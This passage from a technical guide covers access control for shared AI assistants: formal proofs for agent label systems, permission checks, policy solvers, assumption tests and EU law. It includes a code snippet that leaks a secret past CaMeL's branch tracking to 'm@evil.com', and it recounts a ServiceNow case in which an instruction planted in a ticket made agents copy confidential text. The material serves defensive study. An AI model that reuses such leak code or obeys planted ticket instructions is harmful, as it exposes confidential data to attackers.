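Suppose the program answers "yes" 60% of the time and "no" 40% of the time without Birch's files. With them, it answers "yes" 60% and "no" 30% of the time, and the interpreter stops the remaining 10% of runs. Then ω can be 0.6 for "yes" and 0.4 for "no", so the theorem allows this difference. It would not allow a change from 90% "yes" to 90% "no", since ω would have to total at least 1.8. If the program always finishes, both with and without the files, the probability of each answer must be the same in both cases.

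The proof constructs ω with an imaginary version of the interpreter that skips a computation as soon as its label becomes secret. This version gives the same results whatever the secret is, and it produces each observable result at least as often as the real interpreter does.

The theorem therefore doesn't rule out a secret affecting whether a run finishes. In the merger example, Ana could learn one bit from seeing the program stop, and more if she can repeat the run. Garby and colleagues found this problem in CaMeL, the system in which a planner writes code and each value has a record of its source. CaMeL's retry loop ran outside its label tracking, so an attacker could keep trying and collect a secret one bit at a time.

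### Leaks through the choice of branch

FIDES, the label system for agents by Costa and colleagues, gives a weaker guarantee for secrets. According to Garby and colleagues, this guarantee amounts to explicit secrecy, which covers secret data that a program copies or computes with, but not what an observer can infer from the branch the program took. Roughly, if you repeat the exact operations from a run with a different secret, the output must stay the same.

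Suppose a program contains this line:

`if birch_rate > 32: send_email("eva@haulier.example", "Hello")`

The word "Hello" contains nothing from Birch's contract, so the program satisfies explicit secrecy. But Eva learns whether the rate is above €32. If she can choose the threshold for each run and the rate is a whole number from €1 to €64, she can find it in six runs. The program violates full noninterference because changing the rate can change whether the email arrives.

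CaMeL's strict mode tracks branches and blocks that line, but Garby and colleagues show how to get around it with two extra variables:

`rich = True; tmp = True`

`if balance > threshold: tmp = False`

`if tmp: rich = False`

`if rich: send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")`

CaMeL marks a variable as secret only when a branch that depends on a secret runs and changes it. If the balance is above the threshold, the third line never changes `rich`, which stays public and true, and the email goes out. If the balance is lower, `rich` becomes false and no email goes out. Either way, the attacker learns whether the balance is above the threshold. Researchers described this kind of leak in the 1970s. Attempting a proof is a good way to find it, because the step covering the skipped branch cannot be completed.

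FIDES doesn't track branches because tracking them blocks more programs. Its guarantee about untrusted text is stronger than its guarantee about secrets. The guarantee about untrusted text is a form of noninterference, but it covers only one fixed agent loop, not every program an agent might write.

### What LLMbda leaves to the developer

The LLMbda theorems cover the same interpreter that the researchers run, which avoids the usual gap between the system described in a paper and the code that implements it. The network call to the model is outside the proof, which treats the call as one possible source of replies. Tools and data sources also have to be inside the program, which Garby and colleagues list as a limitation. Their tests used a simulated bank that was part of the program, but a real search index would be outside it.

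A program may also endorse untrusted data as trusted. A second theorem guarantees that endorsement cannot release secrets, but not that the endorsed data was safe to act on. On the banking tasks from AgentDojo, the benchmark used to test FIDES, an agent written in LLMbda resisted all but two of 1,296 attacks. In both failures, the user had asked the agent to pay according to instructions in a file that the attacker had replaced. With endorsement turned off, the interpreter blocked this attack, but one model's score on tasks without attacks fell from 36 to 30 out of 48.

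### Proofs about persistent memory

An assistant with persistent memory can save text from one conversation and act on it weeks later. *PerMIT* (Jiang, Bai and colleagues, 2026) limits the agent to seven memory operations. When the agent looks up text that came from outside, it receives a handle, a reference it can pass on but not read. To use the text, the agent has to go through a gate that shows the exact value to a person or another model for approval.

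Jiang and colleagues prove two theorems in Lean for any agent program that uses this interface:

- **Actions:** Every value that reaches a sensitive tool is either something the user typed or something the user approved, character for character, for that tool.
- **Reasoning:** Take two runs with the same typed input and the same random choices but different untrusted memories. If the gate's displays and the user's decisions are the same in both, the agent does the same things in both.

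Hidden text can therefore influence the agent only by changing what appears at the gate or what the user decides there. The first theorem also assumes that each approval is correct, which the proof can't establish. When the researchers set the gate to approve everything, attacks succeeded in up to 10% of cases, depending on the model. None succeeded when a language model judged the requests.

Even a correct approval may be too broad. If Ana approves the haulier's account number for the payment tool in March, the assistant can use the number with that tool again in June for a different purpose. It can also combine two values that she approved separately, without showing her the combination.

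The paper is unusually specific about what Lean has not checked. The main omissions are:

- the full system's handling of batches, in which a user approves many values at once
- approvals that remain valid after the system cancels the action they were for
- comparisons that start in the middle of a run, after the two memories have already diverged
- the whole scheme for sharing approved memories among users, including its probability bounds.

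The supplement gives proofs on paper for these and lists ten differences between the Lean description and the paper's. For example, the Lean version fixes the user's decisions in advance by their order, whereas a real user reacts to the display. An argument on paper covers this difference. Two of the ten make the checked theorems stronger, for instance by letting the attacker control the model that reads untrusted memory.

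Writing the proofs in Lean exposed three errors in the specification. In the first, approving an item changed its label but kept its identification number. That number depended on how many items an attacker had already added, so the agent could learn something about untrusted memory. The corrected specification makes a new copy with a number the attacker can't affect. In the second, the agent received an acknowledgement whenever the user pasted text, even though it was not supposed to know about the paste. The third was a list of cases that wrongly treated "typed" and "approved" as mutually exclusive.

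The proof files are available only on request until the paper is published, so probably few outsiders have checked them. Lean also does not check that a deployed memory system matches the description.

### Permission at the moment of action

An assistant may check permission, spend ten minutes preparing an action, and carry it out after the owner has withdrawn permission. *Temporary Authority, Permanent Effects* (Santos-Grueiro, 2026) proposes checking permission at the commit, the last moment when the system can still stop the change. The check and the change must happen as one indivisible step.

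Suppose Birch lets Ana's assistant send a contract to a bid partner. At the commit, the system needs one justification with five valid parts:

- **Grant:** Birch's approval is still in force and covers this exact action.
- **Premises:** The facts behind the approval, such as the contract's version, have not changed.
- **Dependencies:** Any earlier step, such as a legal review, has finished.
- **Binding:** The file, recipient and operation match the approval.
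- **Eligibility:** Nobody has cancelled the workflow.

All five parts must belong to the same justification. Suppose Birch gives approval 3 for version 7 of the contract. The contract changes to version 8, and Birch gives approval 4 for that version but later revokes it, while approval 3 stays in force. A program that checks each part separately finds a live approval (number 3) and evidence that version 8 is current (from number 4), so it sends the contract. But no live approval covers version 8. The correct condition is

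there is a justification *J* such that every part of *J* is valid,

and not merely that each part is valid in some justification.

Santos-Grueiro proves in Lean that every committed action has such a justification if all protected changes go through the check and each commit is indivisible. Counterexamples show what happens when a condition is missing: an unauthorised action can get through if the system applies an earlier decision after a revocation, or if one piece of code writes without going through the check. These counterexamples can be used directly as test cases.

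When one service approves a change and another makes it, the approving service can issue a single-use reservation. If the reservation lasts τ seconds and each service's clock is within ε seconds of a common time, the other service can use it up to τ + 2ε seconds after issue. With clocks accurate to within one second, a 30-second reservation could therefore authorise an action 32 seconds after issue, even if Birch had revoked permission in the meantime.

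Santos-Grueiro found failures of this kind in 17 security advisories for three agent products, all about flaws that have been fixed. In 12, the approval never covered what the product did. In the other five, something changed after approval. For example, a user approved running a script, and the product ran a rewritten version. Models can't reliably replace the check. GPT-5.6 Sol completed 25 of 36 tasks without authority when permission or another condition changed without notice, and one when it was notified of the change.

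The theorems assume that the approval services are honest and that the policy lists every relevant fact. They do not cover crashes or changes to the policy itself, and there is no proof that the Python services in the experiments match the Lean model. Two prototypes also do not meet one of the conditions for the theorem about versions. The method cannot take back information already disclosed, so a RAG system still has to check permissions on text before the model or the user receives it.

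### Comparing access policies with a solver

The proofs so far take the access policy as given, but the policy may itself be wrong. Cedar is a language for access policies that a program can analyse. A Cedar policy consists of `permit` and `forbid` rules. It allows a request if at least one `permit` rule matches and no `forbid` rule does. A schema lists the kinds of users, documents and actions that the rules may mention. This rule lets people read their own firm's files:

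`permit (principal, action == Action::"read", resource) when { principal.tenant == resource.tenant };`

Suppose someone adds a second rule that lets members of the joint-bid group read any contract. A tester who tries ten users and ten documents might miss the problem. Cedar's analysis tool translates the old and new policies into logical formulas and passes them to a solver, a program that searches for values that satisfy a formula. The solver searches for a request that the new policy allows and the old one refuses. If one exists, the solver returns an example, such as Ana reading a Birch contract unrelated to the bid. If none exists, the tool has shown that the new policy allows nothing extra for any request the schema can describe.

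The solver needs a correct target to compare the policy with. AutoCedar (Vatsa, Shome and colleagues, *AUTOCEDAR*, 2026) builds this target from written requirements before a language model writes the policy. The target has a "floor", which describes requests the policy must allow, and a "ceiling", which limits what it may allow. For Ana, the ceiling would be her own firm's files plus any contract Birch has lent her. A person or another model reviews the pieces AutoCedar uses to calculate the target. When the solver finds a counterexample, the model that wrote the policy has to correct the policy but cannot change the target.

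AutoCedar found a policy that satisfied the target on all 221 tasks that came with one. On 200 tasks with an independently written correct policy, its policy was equivalent to the correct one in 178 cases (89%), compared with 132 (66%) when the same model wrote the policy directly. These results suggest that stating the rule is harder than finding a policy that satisfies it.

Vatsa and colleagues give an example of an error that no later check can find. A band wants to let its members download its album. If the schema gives each user a role called "band member", a member of any band can download it. The solver can't detect this because the schema can't express which band a person belongs to. The same mistake in Ana's system would be a role called "client" with no record of the firm. AutoCedar also does not check actions missing from the requirements, so a policy could allow "export" if the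 requirements don't cover it.

Cedar's result covers only the policy. The search code still has to request a decision from Cedar on every path, with the right user and document, and enforce that decision.

### A correct search may still be unauthorised

Alder may not trust the provider to run the search honestly. A provider could search an old copy of the files or quietly leave out a result. *V3DB* (Qiu, Qu and colleagues, 2026) describes a system that lets a client check that the search was run honestly without seeing the rest of the store.

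The provider first publishes its exact search procedure and a commitment, which is a short fingerprint calculated from a snapshot of the whole index. Changing any record in the snapshot would change the fingerprint. If a client challenges a result, the provider produces a zero-knowledge proof that the result came from running that procedure on that snapshot. The proof reveals nothing else about the snapshot.

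Making a proof takes much more computation than checking one, so V3DB makes proofs only on request. In one test with room for 65,536 vectors, making a proof took 24 seconds and 447 GiB of memory, and checking it took 11 milliseconds. With room for 8,192 vectors, making a proof took 0.8 seconds and 11 GiB.

The proof's public inputs are the commitment, the question's embedding and the list of results, with no user or permission among them. If the snapshot contains both firms' files and Birch's contract scores highest for Ana's question, the provider can return the contract to Ana with a valid proof. Qiu and colleagues leave the choice of an authorised snapshot to the application. The provider could make a separate snapshot for each firm and have a trusted service sign a statement that Ana's searches may use only Alder's.

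The permission check could perhaps go inside the proof. V3DB already pads its index with empty slots and excludes them from the results by giving each slot a score of

*v* × *d* + (1 − *v*) × *d*ₘₐₓ,

where *d* is the distance from the question, *d*ₘₐₓ is larger than any real distance, and *v* is 1 for a real record and 0 for an empty slot. Multiplying *v* by a value that is 1 only when the record's tenant matches Ana's would push Birch's records to the bottom in the same way. The procedure would also have to leave a place empty when too few Alder records remain. Qiu and colleagues have not built this, and it would still rely on correct tenant labels.

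The proof also ends at the search results, so it does not cover any text that other code adds to the prompt afterwards. It does not cover the earlier step that turns Ana's question into an embedding either.

### Turn each assumption into a test

The assumptions behind these proofs overlap, and each suggests a way to look for a failure in the running system:

| Assumption | How the deployed system could break it | Test |
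|---|---|---|
| Labels are correct | Intake files a Birch contract under Alder | Send a marked Birch file through every intake route and compare its label with the file server's records |
| The system knows who is asking | A reused database connection still has Ben's tenant | Alternate rapid requests from Ana and Ben, and look for Birch's canaries in Ana's results |
| All text takes a path in the proof | A new preview service adds text to the prompt | Record the traffic to the model's server and trace every passage to a path in the inventory |
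| Users observe only what the proof describes | A hidden match slows the search or stops a run | Compare response times and failure rates with and without Birch's files |
| The check and the action are one step | Birch withdraws permission between them | Pause the program just before the action, withdraw permission and resume; the action must fail |
| Approvals are correct | A tired user approves everything | Mix known bad requests into a trial and count how many the user approves |
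| The code matches the description | The production code treats a missing value differently | Give both the same random cases and compare their decisions |

The last test is easier when the formal description is a program, as it is for LLMbda and PerMIT. The tester can run it alongside the production code and investigate every difference in their results. In the example, Alder and Birch's provider runs 20,000 random requests through both and finds 14 differences, all involving documents with no tenant label. The description denies access to these documents, but the production database treats an empty label as matching any tenant, so the provider's users are exposed even though the proof is correct about the description.

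The assumptions can still be false after passing these tests. If a random sample of 300 Birch chunks contains no wrong labels, the true error rate could still be about 1%, by the same calculation as for attack probes. In a store with 50,000 Birch chunks, that would be 500 mislabeled chunks that the filter might give to Ana, even if the filter itself has been proved correct. The provider can reduce this risk by checking every label against the file server instead of a sample, which is practical because the comparison needs no model.

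The tests have to continue after the proof is finished. If a developer later adds a cache, Lean will still accept the proof, because the description it relies on has not changed. The provider can require anyone who changes the retrieval code, the login service or the policy to update the description and rerun the proof and the tests before release.

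## Decide who sets the rules, who checks them and who must be told

When the provider of Ana's assistant found that its database treated unlabelled documents as open to every tenant, someone had to decide whether to suspend the service, who should tell Birch, and whether the earlier test results were still valid. Tests and proofs can't settle these questions. Unless the provider and its clients assign such decisions in advance, the engineers who wrote the filter usually end up making them while also trying to finish a release.

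### Five decisions

For the shared assistant, the provider and the two firms might agree on this division:

| Decision | Who makes it | Why |
|---|---|---|
| What the rule for Birch's files is, and its exceptions | Birch's contracts manager | Birch suffers the loss if its prices leak |
| Whether to lend Alder a particular document | The Birch employee responsible for it, in writing and with an end date | The provider can't know what the joint bid needs |
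| Whether the tests are good enough | A tester who did not write the retrieval code and does not report to the manager who wants it released | Builders tend to repeat their own mistakes in their tests |
| Whether to tolerate a known leak | The firm whose files could leak | The provider would be accepting a risk on someone else's behalf |
| Whether to stop a release | The tester or the provider's head of security, each acting alone | A delay usually costs less than a leak |

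The clause comparison, which uses Birch's contracts to answer a question from Alder, shows why someone must be responsible for each exception. Alder benefits, the provider gets a feature to sell, and Birch takes the risk, so Birch must be able to refuse. If the provider's chief executive overrules a decision to stop a release, they should put that in writing and tell the affected client before the release goes ahead.

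*Data Governance for Generative and Agentic AI* (Darapaneni, Padmaja and Gnana Chaithra, 2026) treats authority, enforcement and evaluation as separate functions. A small provider may have to give one person two of these functions, but whoever writes a filter should not be the only person judging its tests. For example, an outside engineer exposed one of the vacuous passes in Hill's program. An independent tester still needs access to the code and the inventory of paths, and permission to switch off checks.

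### An evidence file for one rule

Aircraft and railway engineers often have to justify a claim that no single test can establish. They write an assurance case, which states the claim, the argument for it, the evidence behind each step, and any known reasons for doubt. Missing steps are easier to see in this format than in a folder of test reports.

Here is an extract from an invented file for the specification's first rule, as it applies to Birch's documents:

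| Part | Entry |
|---|---|
| Claim | No Alder employee receives an answer whose context contains a Birch passage that the employee may not read |
| Exceptions | One yes or no per clause comparison, approved by Birch |
| Argument | Eight paths lead to the model or the user's screen. Code checks permission on each. A last check covers the seven paths that build a context; the answer cache has separate entries for each firm |
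| Assumptions | Logins are correct, every chunk has the right owner, and the logs contain every context. On 28 November, a program compared the owner of every Birch chunk with the file server's records |
| Test results | A program that prints its context replaced the model for 120 questions. None of the 40 canaries reached Ana. With the checks off, the same questions retrieved all 40 |
| Disabled checks | Removing the check on vector search, graph expansion, the cache or old messages made a test fail, as did removing the last check. **Not yet tried:** keyword search, tools, previews and the search box |
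| Known leaks | Unlabelled documents were open to both firms until 26 November; fixed, and Birch told. Intake mislabelled a shared mailbox; a person now labels its documents by hand, and Birch accepts the risk of mistakes until 31 March |
| Versions | Retrieval code 5.3, intake 3.8, permission service 2.1, index built on 27 November |
| Expires | 1 March 2027, or earlier if a listed component changes |

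Filling in the "disabled checks" row shows that the provider has checks on eight paths but has tried removing only four of those checks, plus the last check. The last check could therefore hide a fault in the preview service's own check. Before approving the file, the tester can ask the provider to try removing the other four.

The test results cover what the tester did but don't include a failure rate, because 120 chosen questions can't put a limit on what a determined attacker would find. If the provider also has a formal proof, the file should list the proof's assumptions with the other assumptions and give the date each was last tested.

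### Changes that make the evidence expire

A passing test describes the system on the day of the test. The provider can have its release software compare the running versions with those in the file and block the release if they differ. It then has to know which evidence to replace:

| Change | What the provider must redo |
|---|---|
| New connector, for example to Birch's chat system | The path inventory, the ownership comparison and the canary tests for the new path |
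| New or rebuilt index | The ownership comparison, canary tests and timing test |
| New embedding model | The same as for a new index, because the provider has to embed every chunk again |
| New answering model | Attack tests for rules that depend on the prompt |
| New source of permissions | The random permission cases, the withdrawal test and every canary test |

Evidence that a rule is enforced still holds after the answering model is replaced, unless the new model comes with its own memory, web search or shared cache. Each of these adds a new path for data that the existing evidence doesn't cover.

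The fixed end date covers changes that nobody recorded, such as a supplier's unannounced update. There is also a legal reason for it. The European Data Protection Board, which brings together the EU's data protection authorities, warns in its *Guidelines 4/2019 on Article 25 Data Protection by Design and by Default* (2020) that a once adequate measure may stop being adequate as technology advances.

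### When the customer can't see the code

Suppose Alder instead buys an assistant from a large software company for its own staff, and must keep personnel files from everyone outside the personnel department. Alder can't read the retrieval code, replace the model or switch off a check, so the most informative tests are unavailable. Four other kinds of evidence remain:

| Evidence | What it can establish | What it leaves open |
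|---|---|---|
| Canary tests from the customer's accounts | That a leak exists, if a canary appears | Whether code or the model's good behaviour kept the canary back |
| Logs of retrieved passages | That a forbidden passage came up in a search | Anything the supplier doesn't log |
| Contract rights | What the supplier must do, and by when | Whether the filter works today |
| An independent audit | That someone with the code removed checks and saw tests fail | Changes since the audit |

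Canary tests take little enough effort to repeat every week. Alder puts a marked document in every kind of place the assistant reads, then asks the assistant for it from one account that is allowed to read it and one that isn't. Customers reported the failure in Copilot incident CW1226324, so they have reason not to rely on the supplier's monitoring alone. A supplier could make these tests far more informative by offering a diagnostic mode that returns the complete context without calling the model.

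An auditor may have checked only that the supplier has a security policy and follows its procedures. So Alder should ask which access rule the auditor tested, on which version, and whether any test failed when the auditor disabled the check.

The contract can secure much of this. Useful terms include:

- permission to run canary and attack tests
- an export of the passages behind each answer
- notice before the supplier adds a connector or changes a default setting
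- a deadline for reporting leaks, including leaks of purely commercial information
- the ability to switch off one feature and keep the rest.

Alder keeps its legal duties when it buys the assistant. Under EU law, a controller is the organisation that decides why and how to use personal data, and a processor handles the data on its behalf. The EDPB holds the controller responsible for meeting the design duties even when a processor handles the data, and tells controllers to consider this when they sign contracts. In the DSK's *Orientierungshilfe zu datenschutzrechtlichen Besonderheiten generativer KI-Systeme mit RAG-Methode* (2025), Germany's data protection authorities found that RAG can improve the confidentiality of added personal data. But they mostly assumed that one organisation runs the whole system on its own machines, and noted that splitting it among several operators can raise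 further issues.

A small customer may be unable to negotiate with the supplier, but it can still choose which folders to connect. It can leave out the personnel files, for example, if the supplier offers no evidence that the filter works.

### A flaw, or working as designed?

ServiceNow sells software that companies use for support tickets and other internal records. The Hacker News' *ServiceNow AI Agents Can Be Tricked* (November 2025) reported that attackers could exploit the default settings of Now Assist, ServiceNow's AI product, to copy company data and change records. The security firm AppOmni had found the problem, and the two companies disagreed about whether ServiceNow should fix it.

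In the test that AppOmni describes, its researcher Aaron Costello set up two of ServiceNow's standard agents so that only an administrator could use them. One read and categorised tickets, and the other could also create and change records. Using an account that could create tickets but not read other people's, Costello filed a ticket and, in its description, instructed any agent reading it to copy the text of a confidential ticket into this one, and to find another agent if it couldn't do so itself.

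When the administrator used the first agent on the ticket, the agents carried out the instruction, and the ticket's author could read the confidential text. ServiceNow's protection against prompt injection was on throughout. In other tests, Costello got agents to give an attacker administrator rights and to email data out.

Three default settings made this possible. The available models supported "discovery", which lets agents find one another. Agents in the same chat channel automatically joined the same team, and each newly published agent was discoverable.

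Costello and press reports describe ServiceNow's response. The company replied that the system was working as intended. TechRadar's *Second-order prompt injection can turn AI into a malicious insider* reports that it would not change the product but did clarify its documentation. AdExchanger's *How Agentic AI Can Break In The Real World* adds that ServiceNow emailed customers about the risk and credited Costello, but left the feature on by default. This position can be defended, since specialised agents can handle larger jobs by cooperating, they act with the rights of the user who started them, and customers can change the settings. ServiceNow also acted quickly on BodySnatcher, another flaw found by AppOmni, which let an attacker impersonate an account holder using only their email address.

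Costello agrees that the behaviour "isn't a bug in the AI", but argues that customers easily overlook such settings and should have to opt in to communication between agents. AppOmni gains from the publicity because it sells a product that monitors for this behaviour, but it describes the test in enough detail for a customer to repeat it.

Both sides can be right about the facts because they judge the product by different rules. The administrator was allowed to read both tickets, so the check on read access worked. But confidential text reached someone who was not allowed to read it, and text written by an outsider determined which action Now Assist took. Those outcomes break two properties in the specification for Ana's assistant. A customer that had written down the same properties could have tested Now Assist against them, regardless of how ServiceNow described the result.

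Costello told AdExchanger that the only fix was to put a person in the loop, which would undercut the automation. AppOmni itself also advises splitting agents into small teams with narrow tasks, which limits the damage. A permitted-flow check would also have blocked the copy without needing anyone's approval.

The case also shows a limit to OWASP's 2025 guidance, which recommends using several agents, each with only the privileges it needs, when tasks require different levels of access. Separating the agents gives little protection if one with few privileges can get a more privileged one to act for it.

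### What European law requires

The main EU law on personal data is the General Data Protection Regulation (GDPR), formally *Regulation (EU) 2016/679 of the European Parliament and of the Council* (2016). It applies to much of the store because the emails and contracts about pallet rates contain names, even though a pallet rate itself is not normally personal data.

Article 25 requires controllers to build in measures that implement data protection principles "in an effective manner". By default, they may process only the personal data each purpose needs, and this limit also covers who can access the data. The article doesn't prescribe a particular control. The EDPB reads it as requiring controllers to document their measures and be able to demonstrate that the measures work, either with metrics, such as a false negative rate, or by explaining their assessment. Under this broad reading, a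 sentence in a prompt could count as a measure, but the controller would struggle to show that it is effective.

Article 25 places the duty on the controller and does not directly address software makers. A company that uses ServiceNow's default settings is therefore responsible if they expose personal data, even though ServiceNow chose them.

Article 32 of the EU's General Data Protection Regulation requires both controllers and processors to keep personal data secure. The measures it lists include, where appropriate, a process for regularly testing whether the security measures are effective. This is the clearest legal basis for repeating access tests, although the article doesn't say how often to test or who should do it.

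The EU's AI Act has an article on cybersecurity that applies only to "high-risk" systems, such as software that screens job applicants. An assistant that looks up haulage contracts would probably not qualify. The European Commission's *Article 15* requires high-risk systems to be resilient against outsiders who exploit their vulnerabilities, including, where appropriate, through measures against "confidentiality attacks". Providers must state accuracy levels in the instructions for use, but the article does not require them to publish security test results. Fraunhofer FOKUS, a German research institute, interprets the article in a guide also titled *Article 15* as calling for documented cybersecurity tests, updated when necessary.

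These duties do not apply yet. The European Union's *Regulation (EU) 2026/1744 of the European Parliament and of the Council* (2026) postponed them, partly because the technical standards were late. The new dates are:

- **2 December 2027** for the uses listed in Annex III of the Act, such as recruitment
- **2 August 2028** for AI in products already covered by the EU safety laws listed in Annex I.

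Most systems on the market before the relevant date will be exempt unless their design later changes significantly. Providers and users of high-risk systems intended for public authorities have until 2 August 2030 to comply.

### What the standards add

The best-known AI standards mostly concern management. OWASP classes both the Risk Management Framework from NIST, the US standards agency, and the international standard ISO/IEC 42001 as governance material. They can help a provider assign responsibility and keep records, but evidence that a provider follows them does not show that a particular search filter works.

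OWASP wrote its AI Security Verification Standard (AISVS) to supply the technical detail. Version 1.0 has 191 requirements, each meant to be testable, and one chapter covers memory, embeddings and vector databases. Level 1 requirements are a baseline for every system, level 2 suits customer-facing products and sensitive data, and level 3 is for the highest risks. OWASP recommends at least level 2 for most live systems. Buyers can cite individual requirements in a contract, but they should include the version number because the numbering may change.

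OWASP (2026) also announced in September that it had received the Agent Control Standard as a donation, which is meant to extend its guidance towards enforcement while agents are running. According to Cyber Security News, OWASP's 2026 list of top risks includes the advice to "Authorize Before Retrieval". A provider that follows this advice would still have to test whether its own version of the control works.

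| Text | Status | Control | Document | Evidence that the control works |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| GDPR Article 25 | In force | Effective measures, with access limited by default | A record of the measures, as the EDPB reads it | The controller must be able to demonstrate effectiveness, as the EDPB reads it |
| GDPR Article 32 | In force | Security that fits the risk | None named | Regular testing, where appropriate |
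| AI Act Article 15 | From December 2027 or August 2028, for high-risk systems | Resilience to attack | Accuracy levels in the instructions | None named in the article |
| NIST framework, ISO/IEC 42001 | Voluntary | Management processes | Records of those processes | No test of a specific filter |
| OWASP AISVS 1.0 | Voluntary | 191 technical requirements | Depends on the requirement | A check for each requirement |

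None of these texts prescribes tests, such as replacing the model or removing a check, that would distinguish an enforced rule from one that is only stated in the prompt, so clients who want that evidence have to ask for it.

### Who must hear about a leak

If a leak includes personal data, the GDPR generally requires organisations to report it within 72 hours unless it is unlikely to put anyone at risk, as Mondaq's *Europe's Digital Omnibus* explains. Under a position the EU's member states agreed on 21 October, organisations would report only breaches likely to cause a high risk and would have 96 hours to do so, according to Lewis Silkin's *Digital Rulebook* (2026). The Brussels Times' *New EU data rules promise simpler compliance but raise privacy concerns* reports that negotiations can't start until the European Parliament has agreed its own position, so the 72-hour rule still applies.

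A leak of Birch's pallet rate alone would probably not trigger that duty. So Birch's contract with the provider should set a deadline for reporting any forbidden passage that enters the model's context, even if the model leaves it out of its answer.

### Testers' access, publication and small budgets

Testing an access rule can expose the protected text. A program that prints every context creates a log full of contracts that the tester may have no other reason to see. Under Article 32 of the GDPR, people working for a controller or processor may use personal data only on the controller's instructions, unless the law requires otherwise. The provider can do most tests on a copy of the system filled with invented documents, but some checks need the real store, because invented documents would not have revealed the mislabelled mailbox. In the real store, code can compare labels and report only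 document numbers, and a Birch employee can read any passage that needs human judgement. The provider should set a deletion date for the raw logs and keep only the results in the evidence file.

The evidence file is sensitive too, because its list of known leaks would help an attacker. Birch needs full details of any leak affecting its files, but Alder's staff could use those details to exploit the leak. The provider can tell Alder that a fault exists and explain it after the repair. Withholding these details should not become a reason to hide the whole design, since a sound access check works even when attackers understand it.

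Deciding whether to publish is harder when the supplier doesn't plan a fix. Costello showed ServiceNow a draft before publishing. Waiting for a patch would have meant never publishing, and customers could learn from the article which settings to change, though attackers could also learn what to try. Researchers can reduce that risk by giving the supplier time to warn its customers before publication.

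Small organisations have the same basic duties under the GDPR as large ones. The EDPB accepts a cheaper measure if it is effective, but does not accept cost as a reason for having no protection. A small provider can save most by making the system easier to check, for example with a separate index for each client and no shared cache. Two test accounts and a few canaries in each folder cost little to maintain, and a client's own technician can serve as the independent tester. A provider with many small clients can pay for one audit and share the report with them all. If even this is too expensive for some files, the provider should leave them out of the assistant.
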